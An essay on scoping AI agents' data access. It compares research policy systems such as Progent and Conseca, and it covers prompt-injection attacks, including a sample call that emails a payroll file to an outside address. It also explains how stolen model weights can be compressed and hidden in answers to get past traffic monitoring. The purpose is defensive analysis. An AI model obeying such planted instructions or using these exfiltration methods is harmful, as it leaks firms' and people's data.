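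The search should apply those permissions before it picks the best matches. If it picks the ten closest passages first and then removes the forbidden ones, the user gets nothing when all ten are forbidden, even if the eleventh would have answered the question. The index also has to be updated when permissions change, because an employee who lost access to a folder this morning may still find its contents in yesterday's index. Document permissions normally describe everything the user may see, which for an accountant may be all 40,000 invoices and orders, so the search needs a second filter that limits results to the data the task needs.

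When an agent needs only part of a record, masking removes or replaces the rest before the model receives it. But hiding a supplier's bank details could also hide a common fraud, in which someone sends a genuine-looking invoice with a different account number. It is better to have the database compare the invoice's account number with the one on file and return only whether they match. Masking a database column also leaves the number visible in the scanned invoice, where suppliers normally print it. Software then has to find and mask the number in the text of each document, and it will sometimes miss one.

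### From 91,200 records to 24

The firm can narrow the accounts agent's login in three steps:

| Step | Records the agent can open | Reduction |
|---|---|---|
| Original login | 91,200 | |
| Remove email and payroll | 40,000 | 2.28 times |
| Limit rows to the supplier | 240 | about 167 times |
| Limit rows to the month | 24 | 10 times |

Multiplying the reductions gives the full factor of 3,800, most of which comes from the supplier rule. The first step removes more than half of the records, and probably the most sensitive ones, but it contributes a factor of only about 2. If a firm controls only which tools an agent has, it takes only this first step, and the agent can still open 1,667 times as many records as it needs.

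The first step has to limit the agent's credential as well as its list of tools. If the firm hides the email tool but the login still gives access to the mailbox, an agent that can run its own code may be able to read the emails anyway.

Next, the firm masks the bank details, so the agent gets 24 records with the account numbers removed and a note on whether each number matches the one on file. Finally, the firm sets the token to expire after 15 minutes. Expiry alone would do little, because a thief with the original login could copy all 91,200 records in that time by reading about 101 a second, which a database can easily handle. With the narrower token, the thief gets at most 24 records. The expiry mainly limits what the thief could do later, such as reading invoices that arrive next week or changing the agent's notes. If the harness also stores a refresh token, which it can exchange for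 new access tokens, the firm has to protect that too, because a thief who takes both isn't limited to 15 minutes.

The agent can no longer read the credit note from the previous month, but it can request the note by number. After a check, the firm can add that one record for the rest of the task, bringing the agent's total to 25. Giving the agent access to the whole previous month would be simpler, but it would roughly double what the agent can read.

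### Where to put the checks

A firm can put these checks in the harness, in the tool, in a gateway in front of the service or in the service itself. Surapani and colleagues describe a trade-off in which the closer a check is to the data, the harder it is to bypass, but the less information it has about the task. The invoice database can reliably withhold payroll records, but it may have no record that the agent has just read a suspicious email. The harness may have that record, but can't stop calls that don't pass through it. Surapani and colleagues therefore recommend checks at several of these points.

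Park's *Pwning Agentic AI Part I* gives an example of a limit in the wrong place. Researchers at the security company Trend Micro found that a supposedly read-only tool for connecting agents to PostgreSQL still had a flaw, publicly disclosed more than a year earlier, that let agents get round the restriction. People had downloaded the tool more than 100,000 times, though the download count doesn't measure how many were using it with live data. The tool disappeared from the download site shortly after Trend Micro reported the flaw in January 2026. If the tool had used a database login that could only read, a bug in the tool could not have given the agent permission to write.

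### Permitted queries can still serve an attacker

Park also describes a research scenario, not a reported theft, in which an agent that sorts customers' support requests posts a database's authentication tokens in a public comment thread. The agent uses only its own account and approved tools, so no alarm goes off. Park says ordinary access control can't prevent this, because roles control which tables an agent can open but not which rows. That is true of simple roles, but row rules exist to control which rows an agent can open. The agent also had more access than its task needed, since sorting support requests doesn't require a table of authentication tokens.

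Planted text can still misdirect an agent whose access is right for its task. The accounts agent, with its 24 records, can still follow a planted line that tells it to write a note marking a false invoice as correct. Its task requires it to write such notes, so no access rule can block the false ones without also blocking the true ones.

The narrowing does help with secrecy, particularly when the attacker is the supplier. All 24 records concern that supplier, who already has most of the information in them. This suggests choosing row rules that limit an agent, as far as possible, to records about the outsider whose text it has to read. In another of Trend Micro's scenarios, hidden text in an image of one customer's passport makes an agent leak other customers' records. An agent that could open only that customer's file could not have leaked the others.

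Permissions that are harmless individually can also be harmful in combination. Surapani and colleagues give the example of an assistant that combines a person's calendar, location, email and contacts and infers a relationship that none of these sources reveals alone. Rules that cover each tool separately can't catch this. The alternatives include tracking where information came from and restricting where it can go, limiting the number of queries, and asking a person to approve sensitive conclusions. Surapani and colleagues regard these as open research directions.

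### What Microsoft, NIST and MITRE advise

Microsoft published the most detailed advice of the three in July 2026. It recommends giving every agent its own identity, with a named owner and a written purpose. Each role should match a small task, such as creating a draft ticket, rather than a team or department. A firm should limit roles by location, type of data and operation, and use separate roles for reading and writing. Every service should check the agent's permissions on each call instead of relying on an earlier check.

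Microsoft warns about access that grows gradually. A team gives an agent a broad reading role because it is quick to set up. Later the team wants the agent to fix the problems it finds, so it adds more write access than the fixes require, and nobody redesigns the role. Microsoft recommends reviewing permissions regularly, checking what several roles allow in combination, and practising how to shut an agent off. Microsoft sells identity software for this work, so it has a commercial interest in the advice, but most of it would apply to any company's software.

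NIST, the American standards agency, has not gone as far. *Accelerating the Adoption of Software and AI Agent Identity and Authorization* (Booth, Fisher and colleagues, 2026) is a draft concept paper for a possible project, not a finished standard. If the project goes ahead, NIST intends to produce a practical guide based on commercially available technology, according to Biometric Update's *NIST concept paper explores identity and authorization controls for AI agents*.

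MITRE ATLAS is a public catalogue of attacks on AI systems and defences against them. One entry, reproduced on the website PromptRiskDB, covers agents that have more authority than a normal user or that serve several users. It recommends giving such an agent only the permissions its designated tasks require, and basing access on roles or on attributes such as the type of data or the time of the request. Another entry, on PromptRiskDB's *Technical* page, recommends least privilege and delegated access for tools that several agents share, so that a tool works with the permissions of the agent calling it.

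A tool can follow that last piece of advice by using token exchange to get a new token for the service behind it, with no more authority than the agent had. MCP forbids the tool from forwarding the agent's own token to that service.

Microsoft and MCP differ more on what should happen to extra permissions. Microsoft wants an agent to return automatically to its minimal role when it finishes a task, while an MCP client should keep adding to the scopes it has already requested. MCP's approach interrupts the user less, but Microsoft's is closer to task-scoped access. It also suits the accounts agent better, because next month's check may involve a different supplier and shouldn't start with access to the current supplier's records.

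## Who decides what a task needs, and how well do automatic policies work?

The database rule that cut the accounts agent down to 24 records needed two values, supplier 118 and September. Somebody had to take them from the user's request. That is easy if the request is "check supplier 118's September invoices", but many requests are less specific. *Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) gives the example of a user who asks an agent to carry out the to-do list in an email from Alice. Judging by the request alone, the agent needs only to find that email. Once the agent opens it, the list turns out to require reading recent emails and posting a summary on Slack, a workplace chat service.

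No one could write the right policy from the request alone, and by the time anyone has enough information, the agent is already reading text that a stranger may have planted.

A security expert can't practically write a policy for every request, and a single policy for all requests will be too broad for some and too narrow for others. Several research groups have therefore tried to automate policy writing. In most of their systems, fixed code decides whether each tool call complies with the policy. The systems differ mainly in who or what writes the policy and what information the writer can see.

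### Conseca: one policy, written before the agent starts

*Contextual Agent Security* (Tsai and Bagdasarian, 2025) describes Conseca, a system in which a language model writes the policy from the user's request and information the developer has chosen to trust. In the prototype for Linux computers, the trusted information includes usernames, email addresses, and the names of files and folders. The model that writes the policy isn't given the contents of emails or files, so an instruction planted there can't affect the policy, which stays the same until the task ends.

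For each command, the policy states whether the agent may use it, what pattern its arguments must match, and why. In one example, Alice asks the agent to find unread work emails and reply to any that are urgent. The policy bans deleting emails, but lets the agent send an email if the sender is Alice, the recipient has a work.com address and the subject contains "urgent". Ordinary code checks each command against the policy. If it refuses a command, it gives the agent the reason so that the agent can try something else.

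This example also contains a mistake. According to the written reason, the recipient must be on the list of work users, but the pattern, taken literally, accepts any address that contains "@work.com", including eve@work.com.example.net, an address outside the company. Someone who read only the explanation before approving the policy would miss this. Tsai and Bagdasarian rely on experts, or possibly software, to check that the explanations match the rules.

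In a test of Conseca on 20 file and email tasks, an agent using Gemini 1.5 Pro completed an average of 14.0 tasks with no policy and 12.0 with Conseca over five trials. It completed 12.2 under a fixed policy that banned only deletion, and none under one that banned all changes, because every task involved writing something. The agent failed some tasks under Conseca because the policy blocked harmless steps that weren't strictly necessary, such as creating an empty file before writing a summary in it.

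Tsai and Bagdasarian then planted an email asking the agent to forward all messages about urgent security vulnerabilities to an employee's address. With no policy, the agent forwarded them even when the user had only asked it to categorise emails. Conseca prevented this in every task except one, where the user had asked the agent to perform the tasks in urgent emails. Tsai and Bagdasarian consider forwarding appropriate in that case, but such an instruction lets anyone who can send an urgent email give the agent tasks. The test used only one planted message, so it shows that the idea can work but not how often.

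Conseca can't handle Alice's to-do list well because it has to write the policy before anyone opens her email, a limit Tsai and Bagdasarian acknowledge. Letting the policy writer see more would also give an attacker more ways to influence it.

### Progent: a policy that changes during the task

Progent, in its version of May 2026, also has a language model write a policy from the user's request, but the model can propose changes as the agent learns more. Each rule allows or forbids one tool under certain conditions. In a simplified form of Progent's notation, the accounts agent's policy might be:

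```
allow search_invoices when { supplier == 118 and month == "2026-09" }
allow read_invoice    when { supplier == 118 and month == "2026-09" }
allow read_order      when { supplier == 118 and month == "2026-09" }
allow write_note      when { folder == "checks/118/2026-09" }
```

Suppose the agent makes this call:

```
read_invoice(supplier=118, month="2026-09", number=7)
```

Progent finds the rule for `read_invoice`, puts in the values from the call and sees that both conditions hold. It allows the call. But invoice 7 contains a hidden instruction to email the payroll file to an outside address, and the agent tries to obey:

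```
send_email(to="audit@example.net", attachment="payroll")
```

The policy has no rule for `send_email`, and Progent blocks any call that no rule allows. It normally returns an error message with the reason and a reminder of the user's task, so the agent can go back to checking invoices. A firm can also set it to stop the agent or ask the user.

Now suppose that invoice 7 also refers to a credit note from August, number 5530. The model proposes a rule that lets the agent read that one document. Before the rule takes effect, Progent compares the old policy P with the new policy P′. It uses an SMT solver, a program that works out whether a set of logical conditions can all be true together. If A(P) is the set of all calls that P allows, the change is a narrowing when

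A(P′) ⊆ A(P)

and Progent applies it automatically. Any other change is an expansion and needs approval. Here the new policy allows a call that the old one doesn't, reading document 5530, so somebody has to approve it. If the model had instead proposed limiting the agent's notes to a single file in the same folder, the change would have taken effect at once.

The agent's options can therefore only shrink between approvals, which Shi and colleagues call "monotonic confinement". A planted instruction may lead the model to propose a rule that allows `send_email`, but the rule can't take effect unless the approver accepts it. As a further precaution, Progent first has a model decide, without seeing what the tool returned, whether a tool call might justify an update.

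*Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026), which appeared two months before this version, warned that hostile text in a tool's results could lead Progent's updates to loosen the policy by accident. The comparison prevents this from happening silently, though a careless approver could still allow it. The paper's other objection still applies. Progent controls tool calls, so it does nothing about an attack that only changes what the agent tells the user.

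### MiniScope: permissions calculated from the agent's plan

In *MiniScope*, Zhu, Tseng and colleagues (2025) don't want a language model to write the policy, because nobody can guarantee that it will interpret "least privilege" correctly. In their system, the agent submits a list of the tool calls it plans to make. Software then calculates which OAuth scopes those calls require and asks the user to approve any that the agent lacks. The user can allow a scope once, for the session or always, or refuse it. MiniScope keeps the user's real credentials away from the agent and checks every call.

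The calculation takes some work because several scopes may permit the same call, as is the case for 24 of the 37 calls in Google Calendar. Suppose an agent needs one call to search invoices and another to read them. One scope permits five calls, including both of those. Two smaller scopes permit three and four calls, but each includes only one that the agent needs. Choosing the smallest scope for each call would permit seven calls in total, while the single scope that covers both permits five.

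MiniScope treats this as an optimisation problem. Let xᵥ be 1 if the software selects scope v and 0 if it doesn't. It minimises

Σ cost(v) · xᵥ

on condition that the selected scopes cover every call in the plan. The cost of a scope is the number of calls it permits.

Zhu and colleagues also gave language models the plans and lists of scopes and asked them to choose the least-privileged scopes for each plan. The commercial models found the best answer 70–83% of the time and the open-weight models 20–34%. MiniScope was also faster. On tasks that involved several applications, an agent using it took about 5.2 seconds, compared with 20.5 when a language model chose the scopes.

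They then examined some of the connectors that link ChatGPT and Claude to other services, and found six with more permissions than their tools needed. ChatGPT's Gmail connector, for example, requested scopes covering 50 calls when 32 would have been enough. The extra permissions allowed it to change and delete emails, although its interface only supported reading them.

MiniScope is good at finding the least privilege for the agent's plan, but this may not be the least privilege for the user's task, and MiniScope relies on the user to notice the difference. Zhu and colleagues give the example of a user who asks an agent to reply to an email that contains an instruction to delete it afterwards. The agent adds the deletion to its plan, and MiniScope asks the user for permission to send and delete messages. The user refuses, which saves the email but stops the task before the reply is sent.

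MiniScope also measures operations rather than data. Google Calendar has one scope for reading events on public calendars and another for those on calendars the user owns. Both permit the same calls, so MiniScope treats them as equivalent, though one may reveal far more than the other. A cost based on the number of calls also gives a scope with two deletion calls a lower cost than one with three reading calls. Zhu and colleagues say that developers can substitute another cost model. But *Incomparable Minima in Agent Tool Authorization* points out that they don't discuss whether the lowest-cost answer is unique, so the cost model may be making a choice that "least privilege" leaves open.

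### Other ways to set the limits

*Beyond OAuth* (Sharma, Jiang and colleagues, 2026) proposes PAuth, a system in which each service works out for itself what the user's task implies. Suppose a user asks an agent to pay a quarter of their Citi balance from their Chase account. A language model at Chase turns this request into a formula that sets the transfer to Citi at the Citi balance divided by four. Citi signs the balance it reports, so the agent can't alter it. If the balance is $400, Chase accepts a payment of $100. If the agent tries to pay $101, Chase asks the user. No permission remains after the task.

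This is the most precise of the systems, but probably the hardest to introduce, because every service would need its own language model and would have to receive the user's task. By contrast, a firm could put Progent in front of its own agent's tools without waiting for anyone else.

AgenTRIM, by Betser, Bose and colleagues (2026), audits an agent's tools in advance, then shows the agent only the ones it needs at each step. CapScope, a system for coding agents in *Authority Is Not a String* (2026), turns a prediction of what the task needs into an upper limit on authority before any text from the code repository or the tools is available. Sub-agents can get authority only from within this limit. Noyan's *Dynamic Capability Scoping for Enterprise AI Agents* combines an upper limit for each role, software that classifies the task, and a list of banned combinations of permissions.

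In October 2026, Parkinson, Wang and Mustafa proposed elastic least privilege, which puts a price on authority. An agent starts with a small baseline and can borrow more within limits that its owner sets, paying from a budget that refills over time. The agent can see the price when making plans. The price rises with the power of what the agent borrows, and as the agent gets closer to a banned combination, such as untrusted input, sensitive data, and a way to send information out or change things. If φ is the fraction of the combination that the agent has held in the session, the price is multiplied by 1/(1 − φ). For a combination of three, the multiplier is 1.5 once the agent has held one and 3 once it has held two, and the agent can't buy the third.

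That rule might stop the accounts agent from doing its job. The agent reads invoices that a supplier wrote, compares them with the firm's own orders, and writes notes. If the firm classes its orders as sensitive, these tasks together form the banned combination, and the firm would have to divide the work or have a person write the notes. Parkinson, Wang and Mustafa haven't tested the scheme and call its effectiveness an open question. They also cite an earlier method, risk-aware causal gating, which also penalises high-risk tools when choosing a route through a task.

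The main systems compare as follows:

| System | Who or what writes the policy | When | What it checks | What does the checking |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Conseca | language model with trusted information only | before the task | tool and arguments | fixed code |
| Progent | language model, plus the firm's own rules | before and during the task | tool and arguments, and changes to the policy | fixed code and a solver |
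| MiniScope | solver, using the agent's plan | when a plan needs new permissions | OAuth scopes | fixed code |
| PAuth | language model at each service | when the user submits the task | tool, arguments and the source of each value | fixed code at each service |
| AgenTRIM | audit of the agent's tools | before use and at each step | which tools the agent needs | filter on the list of tools |
| Elastic least privilege | the agent's owner and the security team | in advance | authority requested, authority held and price | the service that issues credentials |

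### Contextual integrity and personal data

All these systems need some standard for what an agent ought to see or do. For personal data, researchers often use contextual integrity, Helen Nissenbaum's 2004 theory of privacy. It holds that information should flow in ways that suit its setting. Whether a flow is suitable depends on the sender, the recipient, the person the information concerns, the kind of information and the terms on which people shared it.

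Suppose supplier 118 is a sole trader, so its bank details are personal data. The supplier gives them to the accounts department to get paid. The department can pass them to its own bank, but not to another supplier who asks for them. A label such as "sensitive" can't capture this difference, because the data are the same and only the recipient differs.

AirGapAgent (2024), an earlier system that Bagdasarian also worked on, applied this idea to what an agent may see. Shi and colleagues say it ensures that the agent uses only private data relevant to the task, but doesn't otherwise control what the agent does. For the accounts agent, checking September's prices and quantities wouldn't justify seeing the supplier's bank details, as long as the database can confirm that the account number matches. Tsai and Bagdasarian extend the idea from flows of data to actions, so Conseca can also restrict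 which emails an agent deletes.

AgentDAM, a 2025 benchmark, tests whether agents that work on websites use personal information only where the task requires it. An agent may need to know something without needing to repeat it. For instance, the accounts agent might have to read that an invoice was late because the supplier was in hospital, but its note should mention only the delay.

*ToolMinimize* (2026) describes software that rewrites an agent's tool calls to remove personal details the tool doesn't need. The evaluation has 90 scenarios, each with a human-readable standard for which details are necessary. But the four "models" are simulations that make fixed changes to prepared tool calls, such as filling in optional fields. The results can therefore show how well the software removes unnecessary details, but not how often real agents include them.

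### How much do the policies help?

Much of the evidence about attacks comes from AgentDojo, a 2024 benchmark. It gives agents everyday tasks in four simulated settings: banking, Slack, travel booking, and an office with emails, calendars and files. Researchers plant an attacker's instructions in the text that the tools return, then measure how often the agent completes the user's task and how often it carries out the attacker's.

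Shi and colleagues also used ASB, a benchmark with ten scenarios and five ways of wording the attack. The table gives the main results for Progent, Conseca, PAuth and MiniScope:

| System | Test | Attack success, without → with | Task completion, without → with |
|---|---|---|---|
| Progent, policy never updated | AgentDojo, GPT-4o | 39.9% → 2.5% | about the same |
| Progent, all expansions approved | AgentDojo, GPT-4o | 39.9% → 1.0% | about the same |
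| Progent, all expansions approved | ASB, GPT-4o | 70.3% → 3.9% | about the same |
| Conseca | 20 tasks of its own, Gemini 1.5 Pro | one planted email, blocked in all tasks but one | 70% → 60% |
| PAuth | AuthBench, built on AgentDojo | all 634 hostile calls blocked | all 100 tasks authorised |
| MiniScope | simulated requests for ten real applications | not measured | not measured |

Ranking the systems by these figures would be a mistake. PAuth, for example, was tested on hostile calls made by changing an amount, swapping a tool or skipping a condition. It identified all of these calls as not fitting the task, but a real attacker might find a way to change the task itself.

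Progent has the strongest results, though the solver did not contribute to the 1.0% attack success rate. In that test, Shi and colleagues approved every expansion automatically to simulate a careless user, so the approval check couldn't block anything. The protection came from the language model, which wrote sensible policies and rarely proposed harmful changes. Attack success fell by 38.9 percentage points, and the first policy alone accounted for 37.4 of them. When a person with good security awareness reviewed the policies, no attacks succeeded. Only 6% of the policy updates were expansions, so this person had fairly little to review once the task began.

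The results also provide little evidence about limiting what an agent can read. For AgentDojo, Shi and colleagues added a standing rule that let the agent use non-sensitive, read-only tools in every task. In Progent, a standing rule that allows a call takes precedence over the task's own policy, so the model couldn't narrow what the agent read with those tools. The experiment therefore shows that Progent can stop an agent from sending money or emails to an attacker, but not that it can reduce the records an agent can read from 91,200 to 24.

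Newer models may have less to gain from Progent. Shi and colleagues found that Claude Sonnet 4, released in 2025, followed 6.8% of the planted instructions without Progent and 0.5% with it. That is still a large relative improvement, but the 39.9% for GPT-4o, a 2024 model, is a poor guide to how current agents behave.

They also left out two AgentDojo attacks that persuade the agent to book a different hotel. This is fair, since the user asked for a hotel booking and no rule about tools can distinguish a good choice from one that an attacker influenced. But the 1.0% therefore applies only to attacks that need a call outside the task, and a false note from the accounts agent wouldn't need one.

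### Where automatic policies go wrong

An automatic policy is limited by how clear the request is. "Deal with supplier 118's invoices" might mean checking them, disputing them or paying them. Sharma and colleagues assume that the task is unambiguous, and argue that ambiguity is a separate problem because OAuth gives too much access even when the request is clear. They are right about OAuth, but PAuth is meant to authorise exactly what the task requires, and this is less useful if the user and the service understand the task differently. Sharma and colleagues suggest having the agent state its interpretation for the user to confirm, as a travel agent reads back an itinerary.

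Hostile text can also get into the material from which the model writes the policy. Progent's threat model assumes that the user's request is always benign. Zhu and colleagues are more cautious, because users may paste text from a website or an email into a request. If a clerk pastes in a message from supplier 118 and asks the agent to handle it, any instruction hidden in the message reaches the policy-writing model as part of the request. Conseca's prototype also trusts file names, so a supplier might be able to influence the policy through the name of an attachment that the clerk saves. None of these systems can detect when an outsider has taken over the user's account, because the outsider then writes the requests.

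Shi and colleagues tested attacks aimed at Progent's updates. They planted instructions telling the model to allow every tool or to permit the calls the attacker wanted, and they also used software that automatically searches for effective wording. Attack success rose only slightly, even when every expansion was approved. This is encouraging, but the experiment tried only three methods, and an attacker can keep trying until something works.

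Wrongful refusals also stop agents from finishing tasks. Conseca's policies reduced the number of tasks completed from 14 to 12, which a firm might accept for payments but probably not for sorting emails. Sharma and colleagues design PAuth so that most mistakes lead to an extra question for the user instead of a security breach. An extra question is safer in any single case, but over hundreds of tasks, users can get into the habit of clicking "allow" if many of the questions are unnecessary.

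Zhu and colleagues simulated about three months of Gmail use to see how often MiniScope would interrupt people. It asked for confirmation in 18% to 60% of requests, depending on the user's habits. One simulated user, who always chose "always allow", faced a few questions at the beginning and none after that, because the agent by then had permanent access to everything it had needed.

*CreepScope* (2026) distinguishes authorising each call correctly from maintaining least privilege over the life of a permission, and a system can do the first without the second. In this case, the agent had a legitimate need for each permission when the user chose "always allow". Its access became excessive because it kept all the permissions after the needs had passed.

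### The case for fixed limits

A language model may answer differently from one day to the next, and a stranger's text can influence it. Fixed code outside the model gives the same answer to the same call, however persuasive that text is. *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization* applies this reasoning in ScopeGate, a control that sits between the model and its tools and blocks any call it can't confirm is authorised. Conseca, Progent and PAuth also leave the final check to fixed code. They use language models earlier, to help decide what the code should enforce, so if the resulting policy is bad, the code will still enforce it.

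A firm can avoid some of that risk by writing a few rules itself. In mandatory access control, an old approach from computer security, administrators set rules that users and their programs can't relax. Progent's standing rules can work this way, because no task policy can undo a standing ban. The firm could ban the accounts agent from opening payroll or sending email outside the company, whatever the user requests. These bans would hold even if the request was ambiguous, planted text fooled the policy writer, or the user approved everything. The firm can write them without predicting what a particular task needs, because they cover only what the agent's job never needs.

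Such rules are too coarse to be enough on their own. Of the two fixed policies in Conseca's tests, one blocked every task and the other let the agent forward the security emails. Sharma and colleagues point out that a cap of $500 per payment doesn't mean an agent may pay $499 when the user asked it to pay $100. A sensible arrangement is for people to write the outer limits and for an automatic policy to narrow access within them for each task. If the automatic policy is wrong, the accounts agent might read another supplier's invoices, but it still can't read anyone's salary.

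Both kinds of policy usually judge one call by one agent at a time, so they can miss harmful combinations. Tsai and Bagdasarian note that rules about sequences of actions could help, but are hard to write because so many sequences are possible. *A Theory of Least Autonomy in AI* (2026) raises a similar problem with groups of agents. Progent and MiniScope focus on what an individual agent may call, but the permissions of different agents in a company can combine. If one agent can read payroll and leave files for another that can send email, the company may have a leak that neither agent's policy reveals.

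### No agreed way to measure success

The research groups don't agree on what a good policy would achieve. Shi and colleagues count successful attacks, Zhu and colleagues count the calls that a set of scopes permits, and Sharma and colleagues count hostile calls blocked. Some tests also avoid the hardest cases. *Incomparable Minima in Agent Tool Authorization* reports that when Yang and colleagues built scenarios about how agents choose tools, human reviewers discarded any in which it was unclear which tool had more privilege. This makes scoring more reliable, but real policies have to deal with unclear cases too.

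The obvious way to evaluate a data-access policy is to compare how many records the agent could open with how many the task needed, and to count how often the policy stopped the agent from finishing. None of the evaluations in the table compares the numbers of records, so they can miss a large excess of access. If the firm's invoice service has only one scope for reading, MiniScope would select that scope for the accounts agent and correctly report that no smaller set of permissions would work. It would measure no excess, even though the agent could open all 40,000 invoices and orders when the task needed only 24.

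## How can an outsider obtain an agent, and what do they then hold?

A policy like Progent's works only while the firm's software checks each of the agent's calls. An outsider who copies the model and runs it elsewhere is free of the policy but has no login to the firm's database. If they instead take over the running agent, they have its login, but the policy usually still applies.

What the outsider can do next depends on what they have taken:

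| What the outsider has | Use of the agent | The firm's data | Can they retrain the model? | Can the owner cut them off? |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| A session or token | while it lasts | whatever it opens | no | yes |
| Instruction and memory files | only after adding a model | whatever the memory holds | no | only from services that tokens in the files open |
| Weights | only after adding a harness | only what the model learned in training | yes | no |
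| A device with the model on it | yes | whatever is on the device or open to its tokens | yes | only from services its tokens open |
| Answers collected by using the service | an imitation | none | only the imitation | only from asking more questions |

An outsider who steals a session with a hosted model doesn't get the weights, so they can't retrain the model unless the account includes a fine-tuning service. They can download an open-weight model without stealing anything. In *Securing AI Model Weights* (2024), the American research organisation RAND sees no value in guarding particular copies of a model once it is public.

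### Taking over a session or token

An agent that uses a hosted model normally has at least two kinds of credential. The harness uses one to call the model and others to reach the firm's data, such as a token for reading invoices. An outsider who steals only the model credential can use the model at the firm's expense but can't read the invoices, which requires the invoice token. That token alone is enough to read whatever it gives access to. An outsider who takes over the whole session can use both kinds of credential, as well as the agent's instructions and memory.

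If an outsider takes over a clerk's account for directing the accounts agent, they can ask for summaries of invoices or have the agent write false notes, and these requests will look much like ordinary work. But the outsider can't alter the model. CBS News' *Open-weight AI models are more vulnerable to manipulation and can lack oversight* contrasts Claude, whose weights users can't modify, with models that people run on their own hardware. A provider can also watch for misuse and close accounts, as Anthropic has done, whereas only the firm can notice misuse of a model it runs itself.

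Taking over a session with a self-run model doesn't normally give the outsider the weights either. But an agent with a tool for reading any file on its server might be able to open the file that contains its own weights. The accounts agent doesn't need such a tool, so under ordinary least privilege it wouldn't have one, and the outsider couldn't get the weights this way.

The defences are mostly the ones that limit tokens: short lifetimes, private keys tied to each token, and fresh approval for risky actions. A second login factor, such as a code on a phone, protects the login, but a thief who takes a session token afterwards may never have to enter the code. The owner can end this kind of capture by cancelling the session and its tokens, though that won't recover any records the outsider has already read.

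### Copying the agent's files

The files around the model can reveal a good deal about the firm. The accounts agent's memory might include a year of notes on disputes with suppliers, even if its current token gives access to only 24 records. An outsider who copies the files still has those notes after the token expires.

It is less clear how much of the agent's ability comes with the files. Lyu, Wu and colleagues (2026), in *From Service Access to Capability Theft*, tested this with skills, which are packages of written procedures, scripts and reference material that an agent uses for a particular kind of task. Four strong agents completed an average of 76.1% of the test tasks with their own skills. A weaker agent, built on the open-weight model Qwen3.6-35B-A3B, completed 21.1% without skills and 30.6% with the strong agents' skills. The remaining gap is probably larger than usual, because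 the researchers chose kinds of task that the strong agents could do and the weaker one couldn't, even with the same skills.

A thief doesn't have to use a weaker model, though, since two of the strong agents ran on Claude Opus 4.8 and GPT-5.5, which paying customers can use. Lyu and colleagues recovered the skills without breaking into anything, by asking the agents about them through the normal interface. When the strong agents used the recovered text in place of the original skills, they still completed 76.1% of the tasks. So a thief who copies an agent's files and subscribes to the same model may get an agent about as good as the original, but without the firm's logins. The provider can still close the thief's account, and the thief can't retrain the model.

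If an outsider can prompt an agent to reveal its instructions, the firm shouldn't rely on keeping them secret. It makes more sense to keep tokens and passwords out of the files, delete memory the agent no longer needs, and encrypt the rest.

### Taking the weights from a server

Stealing weights is more valuable because the thief skips the cost of training. RAND cites an estimate of $78 million for training GPT-4. To run stolen weights, a thief needs only suitable computers and the model's architecture (the plan of how its layers fit together). RAND thinks a thief might infer the architecture from the weights.

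The main obstacle is that the weights of leading models are large. A terabyte is 10¹² bytes, so at 10 megabytes a second it takes

10¹² ÷ 10⁷ = 100,000 seconds

to send, or about 28 hours. Compressed tenfold, it takes 2.8 hours. A security team might notice an unexplained transfer that lasts more than a day, and would have much less time to notice the shorter one.

Brown, Rivera and colleagues (2026), in *Aggressive Compression Enables LLM Weight Theft*, study a harder version of the problem for the thief. They assume that the attacker has already broken into the server and can read the unencrypted weights, but can't walk out with a USB drive. The owner inspects all outgoing traffic to check that it looks like normal answers to users. The attacker therefore opens many fake accounts and hides pieces of the weights inside the answers those accounts receive, for example through slight changes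 in the choice of words. The time this takes, in days, is

T = (M × c) / (E × N × s)

where M is the size of the model in bits, c is the fraction left after compression, E is the number of bits each user receives per day, N is the number of fake accounts, and s is the share of each answer that can carry hidden data.

Brown and colleagues assume a model with 1.8 trillion weights of 16 bits each, or 3.6 terabytes. They set upper limits of 200,000 fake accounts and one hidden bit in ten. With those values, the formula gives these times for four kinds of service:

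| What an average user receives | No compression | Compressed 32-fold |
|---|---|---|
| Text | 6,000 days | 188 days |
| Text and images | 118 days | 3.7 days |
| Text, images and voice | 5.9 days | 4.5 hours |
| Text, images, voice and video | 3.7 hours | 7 minutes |

Brown and colleagues say that compression cuts the time needed to steal a model from months to days. That fits a service that sends text and images, but the type of output matters even more than compression. Stealing the model through text alone would take over 16 years without compression and about six months with it. The number of accounts matters just as much. With 2,000 fake accounts instead of 200,000, every time in the table would be 100 times longer.

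An attacker's chance of stealing the model undetected is (1 − p)ᵀ, where p is the chance that the owner detects the attack on any given day and T is the number of days the theft takes. Brown and colleagues set p at 0.1%. For the service with text and images, the attacker would then succeed 89% of the time without compression and 99.6% with it, so compression mostly saves time. If p were 1%, compression would raise the attacker's chance from about 31% to 96%. Real attackers might do worse, because the formula assumes that sending more data per day doesn't make detection more likely, and it ignores the computing work of compressing the model on the victim's server, which the owner might notice.

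### How far can a thief compress a model?

Companies compress models to make them cheaper to run, so the compressed version has to work quickly and well, whereas a thief can accept a damaged model and repair it later. Brown and colleagues split each layer's weights into small groups, worked out a limited set of typical groups, and replaced each group with the index number of the closest typical one. They repeated this on the remaining error up to four times. To recover the model, they rebuilt approximate weights from the index numbers and trained the result for a while.

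Brown and colleagues tried this on Qwen2-1.5B, a small model with 1.5 billion weights, and reduced it from 16 bits per weight to 1.15. They call this 16-fold compression, though 16 divided by 1.15 is nearer to 14. The repair training used 1 billion tokens of text, roughly 0.01% of the amount in the model's original training. On MMLU, a multiple-choice test of general knowledge, the repaired model scored 54.9%, compared with 56.5% for the original. Random weights given the same repair training scored 25.6%, about the same as guessing, so the ability must have come from the stolen weights.

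The other results are less clear. At 0.58 bits per weight, close to the 32-fold compression in the table, the small model's score fell to 48.4%. A model with 7 billion weights fell from 70.5% to 48.5% at 1.52 bits, though it had only a twentieth as much repair training. Brown and colleagues also say that attackers could reach 100-fold compression. Their main evidence is that the weights of a much larger model, Llama-3-70B, stayed close to the originals when compressed to 0.1 bits each. They didn't run full evaluations on that model, so we don't know how well it would work after such a theft.

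### Defences against smuggling

Brown and colleagues tried three changes to the weights. The first, extra training, made the weights only 3–10% harder to compress.

They also examined a "moving target" defence, in which the server keeps rearranging the weights so that pieces stolen on different days don't fit together. In part of each layer, two weight matrices Q and K affect the result through the product QᵀK. The owner can pick any invertible matrix O, replace Q with O⁻ᵀQ and K with OK, and get the same product:

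(O⁻ᵀQ)ᵀ(OK) = QᵀO⁻¹OK = QᵀK

The model behaves exactly as before, but its stored numbers are different. Because the product never changes, an attacker can use it to work back to a standard arrangement. Brown and colleagues did this for one layer and got it working inside a smaller model after only tens of training steps. Rebuilding an entire model this way proved much harder, so the defence may still slow an attacker down.

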